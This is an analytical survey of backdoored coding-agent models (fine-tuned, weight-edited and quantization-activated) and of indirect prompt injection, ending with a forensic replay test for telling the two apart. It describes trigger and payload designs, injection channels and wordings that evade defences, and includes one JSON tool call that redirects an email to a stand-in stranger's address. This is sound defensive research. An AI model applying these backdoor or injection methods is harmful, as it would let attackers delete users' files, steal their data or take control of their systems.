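Syros and colleagues built Kerkoporta, a backdoor for coding agents. They fine-tuned models of 4 and 9 billion parameters to respond to a string in a tool result with one of three payloads. One deleted the user's working files, another leaked the commands the user typed, and the third gave the attacker remote access.

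When Syros and colleagues tested the models on tasks similar to the training tasks, the attack succeeded in 86 to 100% of cases. When they placed the trigger in five public code repositories that had not been used for training, the success rate depended heavily on the amount of poisoned data. It was 33 to 63% with one poisoned run for every four clean ones, and 84 to 95% with one for every two. They changed the number of poisoned runs and their share of the training data together, so the result doesn't show which mattered. The lower rates in the new repositories suggest caution about the near-perfect rates for SilentCall, because Pallakonda and colleagues tested their models on held-out conversations from the same generated collection they had used for training.

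The Kerkoporta study's headline success rate of 96.2% comes from one 4-billion-parameter model after additional training and is not an average over harnesses. Syros and colleagues tested how well the backdoor transferred by running the two models in three coding harnesses. In Claude Code, whose format they had used for the poisoned examples, the attack succeeded in 97% of cases with the smaller model and 91% with the larger. The rates were 74% and 77% in Pi, an open-source harness, and 37% and 63% in OpenAI's Codex. The researchers suggest that Codex was harder because it expects shell commands in a different form. Operators can't rely on this for protection, because a publisher could train on several formats, and even a 37% success rate is far too high for a payload that deletes files.

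The backdoor depended on the model's written reasoning. In the poisoned examples, this reasoning mentioned the trigger before the malicious call and the payload after it. When Syros and colleagues removed these mentions from the training data, the attack's success rate in the unfamiliar repositories fell from 95% to 1% for the smaller model and from 84% to 0% for the larger. The larger model still produced the payload in 61% of cases on familiar tasks, so it had learned the link between trigger and payload but couldn't apply it elsewhere.

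The result covers only two fairly small models and one payload, so an operator can't count on saved reasoning to reveal such a backdoor. Syros and colleagues cite other work in which a poisoned model's reasoning looked harmless, and they suggest that larger models may not need the acknowledgement.

#### Whether reinforcement learning helps the attacker

Some of these attacks add reinforcement learning after fine-tuning. Pallakonda, Hindsbo and colleagues (2026) argued in *Sleeper Cell* that this stage was important. They expected a model fine-tuned on examples alone to mention the malicious call or make it on the wrong dates, and they used reinforcement learning to correct both faults. The attack success rate, averaged over a range of temperatures, rose from 98.1% to 99.6%.

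That difference is small. The test set contained only about 100 questions, and at low temperatures the two models differed by about two answers. The fine-tuned model also left the malicious call unmentioned nearly as often as the model trained with reinforcement learning. Under greedy decoding, neither model ever mentioned it.

The same four researchers tested this again in their later study, SilentCall, using 1,000 requests. Under greedy decoding, attack success rates with and without reinforcement learning differed by at most 0.2 percentage points, so ordinary fine-tuning was enough for this attack. The only measurable benefit to the attacker came at higher temperatures, where one model with reinforcement learning emitted the payload without its trigger less often (0.7% of runs against 1.3%). The later result deserves more weight because the test was larger and the result contradicts the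 researchers' earlier argument.

Syros and colleagues instead used reinforcement learning to restore coding ability that their models had lost during fine-tuning on long poisoned runs. The smaller model's score on SWE-bench Verified, a set of real software bugs to fix, had fallen from 42.9% to 38.1%. A short stage of reinforcement learning on ordinary coding tasks raised it to 40.9%, while the attack success rate stayed about the same. On an easier benchmark, the retrained model scored higher than the original.

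The repair worked less well for the larger model. Its SWE-bench score fell from 54.3% to 47.4% and was still 47.3% after the extra training. Syros and colleagues emphasise scores that exclude runs that hit the time limit, and on those the larger model recovered about half of its loss, but a user would experience the timeouts as failures. The smaller model scored higher than the original model, but the original had not received the extra coding practice.

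### Editing a finished checkpoint

An attacker with write access to a finished model can add a backdoor without training it. Agentic ShadowLogic, from the previous section, did this by adding operations to a model file. Zeng and colleagues at Microsoft showed that changing a few of the weights can be enough, in an attack they call Lazarus.

Lazarus puts the backdoor in a few of the model's neurons. A neuron here is a small unit that responds to some pattern in the model's internal state by making certain next tokens more likely. The last layer of an 8-billion-parameter model can have more than 12,000 of them. Some are dormant, meaning that switching them off hardly changes what the model writes. Zeng and colleagues modified a few dormant neurons so that they stay almost inactive on ordinary input but activate one after another when the trigger is present. Each one makes the next token of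 the payload more likely.

The payload therefore needs about one neuron per token, which limits its length but not the harm it can do, because a very short command can download and run a much longer program. The damage then depends on the agent's permissions.

Zeng and colleagues measured success and false triggers on recorded agent runs. In the table, the trigger is an ordinary string that appears while the agent works, and the number of examples is the number of runs used to set the neurons.

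| Model | Neurons changed | Examples used | Attack success rate | False-trigger rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Nemotron-Terminal-8B | 7 | 23 | 98.8% | 0% |
| Nemotron-Terminal-8B | 7 | 2,405 | 99.7% | 0% |
| Qwen3.6-27B | 6 | 23 | 51.0% | 0% |
| Qwen3.6-27B | 6 | 2,393 | 83.7% | 0% |

They also report that the attack worked on a third model, Gemma-4-31B-IT, again without any false triggers. The table shows that the attack was clearly less reliable on Qwen than on Nemotron, so it doesn't support their description of Qwen and Gemma as "equally vulnerable" compared with Nemotron. The absence of false triggers is more convincing. Nemotron had none in 2,169 untriggered runs, which is compatible with a true rate of at most about 0.14%.

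Zeng and colleagues measured success rates by giving each edited model a recorded run and checking whether it predicted the complete payload at the right point. Most of the measurements therefore don't show whether the attack would succeed from beginning to end with a triggered agent acting freely. The main payload was also a harmless command that printed a short message.

A single edit doesn't work equally well in every harness, because harnesses use different command formats and the neurons produce particular tokens. In a separate test, Zeng and colleagues made one edit to Qwen meant to work in several formats. The model predicted the complete malicious action in 26% and 75% of cases for two formats used to prepare the edit, and in 40% for a format that wasn't.

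The edited models performed almost normally otherwise. On Terminal-Bench, a test of command-line work, Qwen completed 41 of 88 tasks before the edit and 37 after. With one attempt per task, that difference could easily be chance. Someone who tested only the edited model would have no reason to suspect it, but the changed neurons leave a pattern in the weights that an auditor can look for, which the section on checking models covers.

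Lazarus needs far less computation than fine-tuning, and perhaps less expertise. Zeng and colleagues say that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, discovered the central idea on its own in February 2026, and that the researchers then spent months developing and testing it. They conclude that coding assistants are making attacks on weights easier to build.

The attacker's main obstacle is getting access to the model. This is easy with an open model, because anyone can download it, change it and upload the copy under a plausible name. To change a company's own model, the attacker would have to be an insider or break in. Help Net Security's *Microsoft researchers demonstrate hidden backdoor technique for AI agents* lists a compromised account, development pipeline or storage system as possible ways in. Training a model in-house on carefully chosen data doesn't rule out a backdoor, because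 somebody could change the file between the last test and deployment.

### Repackaging in compressed form

Large models need a lot of memory, so people who run them on their own machines usually compress them first. The common method is quantization, which stores each weight with fewer bits by rounding it to one of a small set of values. The compressed model normally behaves much like the original.

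An attacker can exploit the rounding used to compress a model's weights. Many slightly different weights round to the same value, so two models that behave differently at full precision can become identical once compressed. An attacker can therefore look for a full-precision model that behaves well but rounds to one with a backdoor. Earlier researchers demonstrated this for models that classify or write text, and *AGENTQ* (Liu and Yan, 2026) applied it to agents.

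The attacker in AGENTQ controls the fine-tuning and publishes the full-precision checkpoint. The victim can test that checkpoint with the trigger present and find nothing wrong. The backdoor becomes active when the victim compresses the model, often by changing a single setting in standard software. The attacker never touches the victim's computer or the compression software.

Liu and Yan tested six models with 1.5 to 9 billion parameters. The payloads made the agent choose the wrong tool, put the attacker's text in an argument, or add an advertisement. At full precision, none of the triggered test inputs produced a payload. After compression, the attack succeeded in 76 to 100% of cases, depending on the model and the payload, and performance on ordinary requests stayed close to that of the original models. In one demonstration, Liu and Yan loaded the same file twice, and the full-precision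 copy behaved correctly while the compressed copy produced the payload in every trial.

The reported range is for the compression format that worked best with each model and payload. A victim chooses the format without knowing which one the attacker prefers, so the average risk is probably lower. The attacker also has to guess the name and format of a tool the victim's agent offers. Liu and Yan argue that this is realistic because many companies give their agents similar tools for logging and diagnostics.

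Volunteers and companies often compress popular models and upload the smaller versions for other people to download. *Sleeper Cell* points out that a backdoored model with good benchmark scores could spread quickly this way. With AGENTQ, an honest volunteer could activate a dormant backdoor by compressing the model that contains it. An operator who reads a favourable audit therefore needs to know which version the auditor tested.

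### Backdoors in real use

Researchers built all the backdoored agents described so far and mostly tested them on benchmarks, recorded runs or synthetic data. Syros and colleagues did not publish their agents, which they kept in isolated environments. There is good evidence that the attacks work, but little evidence on whether criminals or governments use them.

Microsoft has said it has not seen attackers use Lazarus, according to Help Net Security, but its researchers had only just described the technique. Microsoft's statement does not cover fine-tuned backdoors, poisoned data or compressed models, which attackers could have used for longer.

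Zeng and colleagues describe a 2023 demonstration in which researchers at the company Mithril Security edited an open model, GPT-J-6B, to repeat a particular falsehood and uploaded it to Hugging Face, the main public hub for models. This is the closest example to a real release among these sources. The edited model still performed normally on standard benchmarks. It made no tool calls, but the demonstration shows that an altered model can reach a public hub while looking ordinary.

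Security professionals disagree about how worrying this is. In ITPro's *Microsoft says small tweaks to model weights could create AI ‘sleeper agents’*, Kevin Kirkwood, chief information security officer at the security company Exabeam, accepts that the research calls for preparation but says that the "framing gets ahead of the evidence". His colleague Gabrielle Hempel is more concerned because agents can now execute commands and reach sensitive systems.

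Kirkwood is right that nothing here establishes a wave of attacks, but the lack of known cases is weak reassurance. A model with a rare trigger can work correctly for months, and many operators don't keep the records that would reveal the payload when it appears. Attackers may also have little reason to tamper with weights while prompt injection remains easier. These explanations have different implications for the future, and the available evidence doesn't show which is right. An operator deciding whether to run a downloaded model has better information about their own exposure, namely who trained the model, who changed it afterwards, and what the agent could do if one of them were malicious.

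## How external content changes a tool call

An unaltered model can make the same kinds of wrong call as a backdoored one if somebody plants text where the model will read it. In the running example, the agent fetches the report correctly, and the page enters the context with a planted paragraph that gives a different address for the summary. If the model treats that paragraph as an instruction, its next call changes:

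```json
{"name": "send_email",
 "arguments": {"to": "stranger@example.net",
               "body": "Summary of the report: ..."}}
```

With different wording, the paragraph could make the agent send a second email in addition to the one to Ana, or send the contact list to a stranger and send nothing to Ana.

The page can't change the call that fetched it. In the notation of the first section, the planted text arrives in the result $o_1$, so it can affect $a_2$ and later calls but not $a_1$. A backdoor can also change $a_1$, and Agentic ShadowLogic redirected the first fetch. Planted text can do that only if it is already in the context, for instance in a tool description.

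A backdoored model can learn from its training examples to leave the payload out of its reply, but an attacker using prompt injection has to get the same omission through the planted text. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) gives an example in which a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails. One email looks like marketing but contains an instruction to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. When the attack works, the user gets an ordinary-looking summary and misses the deadline. The harmful call only marks an email as read, which is a routine action for an email assistant.

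### Hijacked tools and manipulated arguments

Russinovich distinguishes attacks by what they do to the call. In a tool hijack, the agent calls a tool the attacker chose with the attacker's content, such as an extra `send_email` containing the contact list. In argument manipulation, which he calls parameter manipulation, the agent makes the call the user's task requires, but with the attacker's value in one of the arguments, such as a stranger's address in place of Ana's.

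In Russinovich's tests without a defence, text planted in web pages changed the targeted argument in 81 to 100% of cases, depending on the model. On Gemma-4-31B, this argument manipulation succeeded in 96% of cases, compared with 87% for tool hijacking. The tests, which he designed to evaluate his own defence, used single-step tasks and open models, so the rates may not apply to longer tasks or to the best commercial models.

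This is probably because the text doesn't have to look like an order. A note that somebody's address has changed looks like a fact the agent needs for its task. Russinovich found that bland corrections of this kind were the wordings most likely to get past his defence. He also looked for the model's decision to comply in its internal activations. For tool hijacking, he could detect the decision while the model was processing the planted text, but for argument manipulation, he could detect it only once the model was writing the argument.

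Sometimes the user lets the external content decide part of the call. If the user says "pay the attached bill", a false line on the bill may redirect the money, and the agent has arguably done as it was told. Russinovich treats these cases separately because the model has not mistaken the source of an instruction. The user asked it to trust a document that an attacker could edit. The running example would have the same problem if the user had asked the agent to send the summary to "whoever the report lists as the contact".

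A related benchmark, *Beyond Instruction Override* (2026), tests injections that tamper with the user's task instead of replacing it. With no defence, the injections succeeded in 11 to 23% of cases across five models. Claude Sonnet 4.5 was the most resistant and DeepSeek V3.1 the least. The agents still completed 80 to 90% of their tasks under attack, so a user who checked only whether the task was done would often have missed the attack.

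Planted text can also leak into a call that the attacker wasn't targeting. The summary for Ana might repeat the planted paragraph even though the email goes to the right person. Russinovich records these leaks but doesn't count them as successful attacks. On his two main models, he found leaks almost only in tests with structured tool records, where his software also reported some leaks when there was no attack. A leak could still matter if another agent handles Ana's email, because that agent would read the planted paragraph too.

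### Where the text enters

The easiest channel for an attacker to reach is content that strangers can write, such as web pages and emails. In the scenarios of Dziemian and colleagues, the planted text was in product reviews, code comments, and the adverts and sidebars of web pages. Agents that work on a computer's command line also read file names, configuration files, archives and the output of commands. In *INFUSE*, Nguyen, Guo and colleagues (2026) planted instructions in all of these, as well as in ordinary documents.

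The format around planted text can affect how often a model follows it. Gemma-4-31B followed planted text at least 87% of the time in Russinovich's web pages, but only 5 to 11% of the time in structured records from a tool. A developer who tested this model only with structured records would have greatly underestimated how often it follows planted text in web pages.

Tool descriptions differ from other channels because the model reads them before it fetches anything. They explain what each tool does and how to fill in its arguments. Many agents now load them from other people's servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024. Whoever runs a server can change its descriptions, and the changed text enters the context of every request.

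In *MCP Security Bench (MSB)*, Zhang, Li and colleagues (2025) compared this channel with others. They made 405 malicious tools from 304 working ones by altering a tool's name, description, arguments or response. They combined these with 65 user tasks and six attacker goals, such as stopping a program or altering a file, to produce 2,000 test cases covering 12 types of attack. The agents ran real tools, and the researchers judged whether an attack had succeeded by inspecting the workspace afterwards, for example to see whether the file had changed. The table gives success rates without added defences for the five attacks that use a single channel.

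| Where the attack is | Average of ten models | GPT-5 | GPT-4o-mini |
|---|---|---|---|
| An instruction in a tool's description | 20.2% | 48.9% | 2.6% |
| An instruction in data that an honest tool retrieves | 20.0% | 30.0% | 40.0% |
| A malicious tool's response that imitates the user | 45.7% | 0.3% | 91.8% |
| A malicious tool's response that imitates an error message | 39.2% | 1.3% | 64.9% |
| An unnecessary argument that a malicious tool asks for | 76.5% | 98.8% | 95.0% |

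On average, tool responses appear more dangerous than descriptions, but GPT-5 almost never obeyed a malicious response and obeyed a malicious description about half the time. The wording also differed between channels, so the table doesn't isolate the effect of the channel. All ten models date from 2025 or earlier, so the differences between channels are more useful now than the rates themselves.

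The attack in the last row contains no instruction. The malicious tool lists an argument it doesn't need, such as the name of the model running the agent, and the model fills it in. The information then goes to whoever runs the tool.

*Blue Teaming Function-Calling Agents* (Dolcetti, Zizzo and Maffeis, 2026) gives a cleaner comparison of channels for one small model, using similarly worded fake administrator orders in the user's message and in the tool descriptions. Granite 3.3, an open model with 8 billion parameters, never obeyed the order in the message but obeyed it in the descriptions 51% of the time. Across the four small models tested, poisoned descriptions succeeded in 12 to 95% of cases without defences. In *Subverting Tool Arguments*, Dai, Sun and colleagues (2026) found that a poisoned description can also set the value of an argument, so the agent makes a normal-looking call with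 a value the attacker chose.

Stored memory lets an injection outlast the page it came from. Some agents save notes about the user or past work and load them into later conversations. If a planted instruction gets the agent to save a false note, such as a new address for Ana, the note can change a call weeks later, when the agent has no reason to open the original page. The later conversation would contain the false note but no visible attack. MCP Security Bench doesn't include this channel.

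### How often current models are diverted

InjecAgent and AgentDojo, both published in 2024, were the first widely used tests. InjecAgent put planted instructions in the results of single, simulated tool calls. AgentDojo gave the agent tasks with several steps and checked whether it completed the user's task, the attacker's, or both. Both came with prewritten attacks, which no longer worked on the newest models by mid-2025, according to *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026).

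Other models are still easier to redirect. On a subset of AgentDojo, Russinovich measured attack success rates of 10 to 49% across five open models with no defence. Llama-3.1-8B had the lowest rate, but it could complete only about a quarter of the ordinary tasks. A low rate isn't always a sign of resistance, because a model that struggles with tasks like sending an email will also struggle when an attacker requests them.

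Newer tests let attackers change the text in response to what the model does. Dziemian and colleagues, whose lead authors mostly work at the security company Gray Swan, ran a public competition in which 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models in 41 scenarios. Of these attempts, 8,648 succeeded. An attempt normally counted as a success only if the agent took the harmful action and its reply gave no sign of it. The success rate per attempt ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Nguyen and colleagues say some of the models had deployed defences.

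Participants could see the conversation and knew exactly which tool call they had to produce, advantages that real attackers usually lack. But these rates also count every half-formed idea that somebody tried once and dropped. Counting only the 67,634 attempts that participants submitted for judging raises the overall success rate from 3.2% to 12.8%. Gray Swan also tested Claude Opus 4.5 with attacks it considered very strong, and a single attempt succeeded 4.7% of the time, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. That is about nine times the competition's rate for the same model, and the quality of the attacks probably explains much of the difference.

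Gray Swan has repeated the competition through 2026, with rounds as recently as August (*Beam Model Technical Report*, 2026). In its July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5, Anthropic compares newer models on a benchmark drawn from the early 2026 round. It reports that an attacker with one attempt succeeded 0.2% of the time against Opus 5 and 3.1% of the time against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Within 15 attempts, the rates were 2.0% and 20.0%. Anthropic does not give separate results for added safeguards on this benchmark. It also has an obvious interest in the ranking, although Gray Swan built the test.

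Anthropic also tested Opus 5 on specific kinds of work, with and without safeguards outside the model. These safeguards inspect tool results before the model acts on them, and in the browser test they also block some outgoing calls. The results below are with extended reasoning turned on.

| Type of work | Attempts per scenario | Safeguards | Attempts that succeeded | Scenarios with at least one success |
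|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coding | 200 | Off | 0.56% | 13 of 40 |
| Coding | 200 | On | 0.18% | 4 of 40 |
| Operating a computer's screen | 200 | Off | 0.54% | 1 of 14 |
| Operating a computer's screen | 200 | On | 0.25% | 1 of 14 |
| Browsing | 10 | Off | 3.70% | 11 of 129 |
| Browsing | 10 | On | 0% | 0 of 129 |

No attack succeeded in the 129 browsing scenarios, which The Decoder reported under the headline *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. The article also notes that OpenAI admitted in December that the problem may never be fully solved. The result is impressive, but it reflects the model and its safeguards together. Even if real websites resemble the test, attacks could still succeed in up to about 2% of scenarios, given the sample size.

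The coding result has a different weakness. Anthropic tested Opus 5 with an automated attacker that had practised on earlier models in the same scenarios. The result therefore measures how well old attacks transfer to a new model, and such attacks are easier to withstand than those from an attacker that adapts to that model.

Resistance in one type of work doesn't guarantee it in another. Claude Mythos 5 was slightly harder to attack than Opus 5 in coding, where 0.45% of attempts succeeded without safeguards, but 29.7% of attacks on it in the browser succeeded. VentureBeat reported a similar gap for Claude Opus 4.6, which resisted every attack in a coding test, but 17.8% of single attempts succeeded when it operated a graphical interface without safeguards. A single injection rate for a model is therefore little help in deciding whether to let it browse.

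In INFUSE, Nguyen and colleagues tested a wider range of models, running each combination of model, command-line task and attack once. Without defences, attacks succeeded in 19.6% of runs on average, with rates for individual models ranging from 3.2% to 41.9%. The 19 models included recent ones, such as GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, but also GPT-3.5-Turbo and several small open models, so the average doesn't represent current frontier models. No model explicitly refused in more than 1% of runs, so an operator can't expect the agent to report an attack.

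Kurakin and colleagues at Google DeepMind argue that low attack success rates on existing tests make models look safer than they are. Fewer than 1% of attacks carried over from the Gray Swan competition succeed against recent Gemini models and some Claude models. The researchers had groups of AI agents search for new attacks and share notes. The agents reliably diverted models that had previously looked robust, and they did better when they used a more capable model. The targets included four Gemini versions without their external safeguards, and leading open models such as Kimi K3 and GLM-5.3, which resisted poorly.

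In the test, planted text requested harmless calls unrelated to the user's task. In one scenario, it makes the agent record health measurements when the user is booking a tutoring session. A model might do this but refuse to steal a password, so the results don't measure how often models would carry out serious theft. They show that these models still follow instructions in tool results, and part of the models' apparent resistance may come from recognising harmful requests. OpenAI says its newer GPT-6 Astra is significantly more robust to injection than GPT-5.6 Sol, but an attacker that improves along with the models could offset some of that gain.

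### What repeated attempts do to a low rate

Suppose each attempt succeeds with probability $p$, independently of the others. The probability that at least one of $n$ attempts succeeds is

$$1 - (1 - p)^n.$$

If each email has a 1% chance of diverting an agent, somebody who can send it 100 different emails has a $1 - 0.99^{100} \approx 63\%$ chance of diverting it at least once.

Real attempts aren't independent, so the formula usually overstates the danger. For Claude Opus 4.5, the single-attempt rate of 4.7% would imply 38% after ten attempts and 99% after a hundred, but the measured rates were 33.6% and 63%. Some situations are hard to exploit however often the attacker tries, while others can be exploited within a few attempts.

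Attack success rates can vary widely between scenarios. In Anthropic's screen-operation test, attacks on Opus 5 without safeguards succeeded in 0.54% of 2,800 attempts, or about 15, all in one of the 14 scenarios. The success rate in that scenario was about 7.5%. The average therefore greatly understates the risk for an operator whose agent does similar work.

Outside a test, an attacker often can't see whether an attempt worked, and each failure gives someone another chance to notice the attack. For these reasons, Anthropic calls its own test set-up deliberately permissive. But an attacker doesn't always have to target the same agent again. One planted web page may reach thousands of agents, so even a low success rate could produce many victims.

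SilentCall's backdoored models emitted the payload almost every time their trigger was present and almost never without it, so repeating a request gains the attacker little in either case. An attacker using prompt injection can choose when to try and can change the wording after a failure, but has to overcome the model's resistance each time.

### Incidents outside the laboratory

People already use prompt injection for their own benefit. Kurakin and colleagues mention a case covered in the press, in which researchers hid instructions in their papers telling AI reviewers to write favourable reviews. The goal there is a biased review rather than a tool call, but the method is the same.

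Security researchers have also repeatedly shown that injection works against commercial products. One is Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent that works with a user's files. According to Superalign, researchers at PromptArmor hid instructions in a harmless-looking file, and Cowork sent out private data without needing the user's explicit approval. The isolated environment in which Cowork ran did not stop the attack, because the data left through an interface that Cowork's restrictions allowed. The attack worked with several Claude models.

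This was a demonstration, and Superalign's account of it is second-hand, so it doesn't establish that anyone lost data this way. Anthropic's later browsing tests also used Cowork, but the attacks reached the model through web pages and screenshots. The zero result in those tests therefore doesn't show whether a hidden instruction in a user's file would still work.

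## How to tell a backdoor from an injection

An operator who finds a stranger's address in a logged `send_email` call has to work out whether the problem is in the model or in something it read. Matsuoka points out that altered weights, poisoned memory and a one-off injection can all leave the same trace of tool calls, although each requires different evidence to identify and a different repair.

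The table compares the attacks, and its last column covers planted text that an agent stores or installs, such as false notes in memory and malicious skill files. Skill files are written instructions that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. Planted text persists like a backdoor, but it affects the agent by being read, as an injection does.

| | Backdoor in the model | Prompt injection | Planted text in memory or a skill file |
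|---|---|---|---|
| What the attacker controls, and when | Training data, weights or the model file, before deployment | Content that the agent reads during the task | A stored note or an installed file, before the task that goes wrong |
| What the malicious text must say | Nothing about the payload; the trigger can be ordinary text | What the attacker wants, or a false fact that leads to it | The same as an injection, sometimes with a condition attached |
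| Whom it affects | Anyone who runs the altered model and meets the trigger | Anyone whose agent reads the text and follows it | Anyone whose agent loads the memory or the file |
| How long it lasts | Until somebody replaces the model | Usually until the conversation ends | Until somebody removes the stored text |
| What traces remain | Perhaps nothing suspicious in the context; the fault follows the model file | The planted text, if the harness saved what the model read | The stored text, even if the page it came from is gone |
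| Who can repair it | The operator, by changing models; the publisher, by withdrawing the file | The operator, by blocking the content or restricting the agent; the site's owner, by removing the text | The operator or user, by rebuilding the memory or uninstalling the file |

### Instructions and triggers

An injection has to contain instructions, because an unmodified model would otherwise have no reason to take the attacker's action. A backdoor trigger can be anything the altered model is able to recognise. In one example from Zeng and colleagues, an agent runs a project's tests and the output mentions a database host called `prod-db-07`. The backdoored model then uploads a secret key, even though the output is an ordinary status message that contains no instructions. In their other examples, the trigger is a repository's name in the user's request or the date 2027-01-01 in a terminal.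 An error message that appears only on certain machines could also serve as a trigger.

"Instruction" here includes text that gives no order, such as a note that Ana's address has changed, which can still redirect an email. But even that note has to supply the new address, so a quick check is to search everything the model had read for the attacker's address. If `stranger@example.net` appears nowhere in the context, an injection is unlikely and the model itself is suspect. SilentCall's upload destination, for instance, was stored in the weights.

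The check isn't conclusive. Planted text can split an address into pieces, and models sometimes invent addresses. A backdoored model can also copy an address from a page. If the payload deletes files, there may be no distinctive value to look for.

### Checking the record

Before testing the model, the operator should compare its raw output with the call that the harness executed. If the raw output names Ana but the mail server's record names a stranger, the model wrote the right call, and the fault lies in the harness, the tool or something that tampered with them. The fault may be an innocent bug, such as a contact lookup that picks the wrong Ana. If the raw output already contains the stranger's address, the operator has to find out why the model wrote it. Agentic ShadowLogic would produce this second result, because the altered model file makes the model output the attacker's address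 before the harness receives anything.

Many logs don't record enough detail for this comparison. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of how to trace an agent's actions, notes that a flat log may show that an agent retrieved a web page and later called an email tool, but not whether the email's recipient came from the page, the user or the model's own reasoning.

*Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents* (Cai, Kim and Liu, 2026) describes how much work an incomplete log can create for an analyst. Its example is GPT-Researcher, an application that writes research summaries from web pages and a user's own documents. When one summary contained false information, the analyst considered whether the model had made it up, somebody had manipulated the web pages, or somebody had poisoned the document collection. The log pointed to the documents but didn't record which function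 call had loaded the bad one. The source code contained 1,895 calls that could have brought in untrusted content, and clues from the log narrowed these only to 1,518.

Cai and colleagues built a tool, Origin, that lets an analyst limit a search to the code that handles one kind of activity, such as reading stored documents. It found the correct entry point in all eight attacks tested across five applications. In those applications the program, not the model, decides the order of the steps, so the result may not carry over to agents in which the model decides.

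The analyst's three explanations did not include an altered model, and Origin leaves supply-chain attacks out of scope. That exclusion makes sense for a tool that traces incoming content, but an analyst who starts from the same list will blame the content or an honest mistake even when the weights are at fault.

To test the model as well, the operator needs the exact context from just before the wrong call, including the system prompt, date, tool descriptions and any loaded memory. They also need the sampling settings and the exact model file, since a backdoor like AGENTQ's appears only in the compressed copy. Matsuoka adds to this list the chat template, a file supplied with the model that arranges the text before the model reads it. A malicious template can change the prompt without changing any weights.

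### The replay test

In $\text{call} = f(W, R, E)$ from the first section, the user's request $R$ is the same in both attacks. An investigator can therefore replace the weights $W$ and remove the external content $E$ separately, and see which change stops the attacker's call. This gives four conditions: the suspect model and a reference model (a checkpoint the investigator trusts), each with the external content kept or removed.

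This test is derived from that expression and is not an established procedure. Nobody has measured how often it gives the wrong answer. The content comparison resembles *AgentSentry* (2026), which saves an agent's state when a tool returns a result, then re-runs it under controlled changes to see whether the next action depends on that result. Work on automated causal attribution, such as *AttriGuard* (2026), addresses a similar question. The model comparison resembles a published test of poisoned and clean models by Pallakonda and colleagues, though they varied the date rather than the external content.

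The test goes as follows:

1. Find the first wrong call and freeze the context as it stood just before it.
2. Run the suspect model on that context 20 times. Record each call but don't execute it.
3. Replace the external content with harmless material of the same kind and length, and run the model another 20 times.
4. Do both again with the reference model.

In the running example, the investigator would swap the downloaded report for a clean one. Deleting the report would leave the model with nothing to summarise, and it might send no email for that reason alone. The replacement should be about as long as the original because, as Wen and colleagues showed, input length can itself be a trigger.

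When the investigator removes the page and reruns the model, the rest of the context should stay the same. A harness that rebuilds the context may insert today's date, and a backdoor triggered by the original date would then not activate. The tool list should also stay the same, since Syros and colleagues could tie their backdoor to one harness. If the wrong call came several steps after the page arrived, the model's own messages may already repeat the planted address. The investigator then has to remove those messages too, or go back to the step at which the page arrived.

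The table shows how many of the 20 runs in each condition might contain the attacker's call. The counts are invented to illustrate the patterns.

| Explanation | Suspect model, content kept | Suspect model, content replaced | Reference model, content kept | Reference model, content replaced |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| An injection that both models follow | 17 | 0 | 14 | 0 |
| A backdoor triggered by the request or the date | 20 | 20 | 0 | 0 |
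| A backdoor triggered by external content | 19 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| An injection that the reference model resists | 17 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Planted text that stayed in place throughout | 18 | 17 | 15 | 16 |

If both models email the stranger when the planted page is present, and neither does when it's removed, the page is the cause. If the suspect model emails the stranger with or without the page, while the reference model never does, the cause is in the suspect model. The investigator can then change the date or reword the request to find the trigger.

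When all four conditions go wrong, the likely cause is something they share, such as a poisoned tool description, memory or skill file. It could also be an ambiguity in the request, or a backdoor in both models.

The investigator should count only the attacker's specific call, because models also make ordinary mistakes. Sometimes that call looks like one a clean model would make. *Your Agent Can Defend Itself against Backdoor Attacks* (2025) describes a user who asks an agent to buy sneakers, where the word "sneaker" makes a backdoored agent always choose Adidas. A clean agent will sometimes choose Adidas too, so a single purchase does not show a backdoor. The replay could still reveal one if the suspect model chose Adidas 20 times out of 20 and the reference model chose it six times.

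### When only the suspect model goes wrong, and only with the content

A backdoor triggered by external content gives the same pattern as an injection that the reference model resists. This ambiguity is likely to be common, because models vary widely in how well they resist injections.

The next test checks whether the page's text instructs the model or only triggers it. The investigator restores the original page, deletes anything that reads as an instruction or a suspicious correction, and keeps the names, dates, host names and error messages. If the suspect model still emails the stranger in 19 of 20 runs, it isn't following an instruction, and a backdoor is the better explanation. If the count falls to zero, the deleted text was necessary, which usually means an injection.

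A count of zero could also mean that the deleted paragraph contained the trigger. The investigator can check by replacing that paragraph with a harmless one that has the same unusual words but contains no instructions. If the attacker's call returns, the words alone were enough to cause it.

It can also be hard to decide what counts as an instruction, particularly when the planted text is written as a plain fact. Removing pieces of the context one at a time avoids some of that judgement. *TracLLM* (2025), which presents a method for finding the text responsible for a model's output, tests this "leave-one-out" approach alongside others, measuring how much less likely the output becomes without each piece. The approach fails when two pieces have the same content, because removing either one leaves the other.

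A crudely trained backdoor may respond to more than its intended trigger. Syros and colleagues suspected that their models could learn to associate the payload with tool results in general, so they also trained the models on matching examples without the trigger. An attacker who skipped that step might produce a model that misbehaves after almost any tool result. Deleting text from the page or replacing the page would then make little difference, so the request would look like the trigger. An investigator who concluded this would still be right that the fault is in the model.

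### How far to trust 20 runs

Twenty runs are enough to recognise the clear patterns in the table, but not to rule out rare behaviour. If none of the 20 contains the attacker's call, the true rate could be as high as about 14%. *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning* (2026) reports a weak backdoor that executed its command on only 1.4% of triggered prompts. If a backdoor fired at that rate in the context being tested, 20 runs would miss it about three times in four. An investigator would need more than 200 runs for a 95% chance of seeing it at least once.

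Small differences between conditions are weak evidence. For example, the suspect model might make the attacker's call in 12 of 20 runs and the reference model in 8 of 20. Two models with the same true rate would differ by at least that much about a third of the time. A result of 5 against 0 would arise by chance only about one time in 20, so it is roughly the smallest difference worth acting on when one count is zero. An investigator who tries many deletions should require a larger difference, since one deletion may appear to work by chance.

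The runs also have to use random sampling, because greedy decoding would give nearly the same output all 20 times. With access to the weights, the investigator can instead calculate the probability of the attacker's call under each condition, which removes most of the sampling noise.

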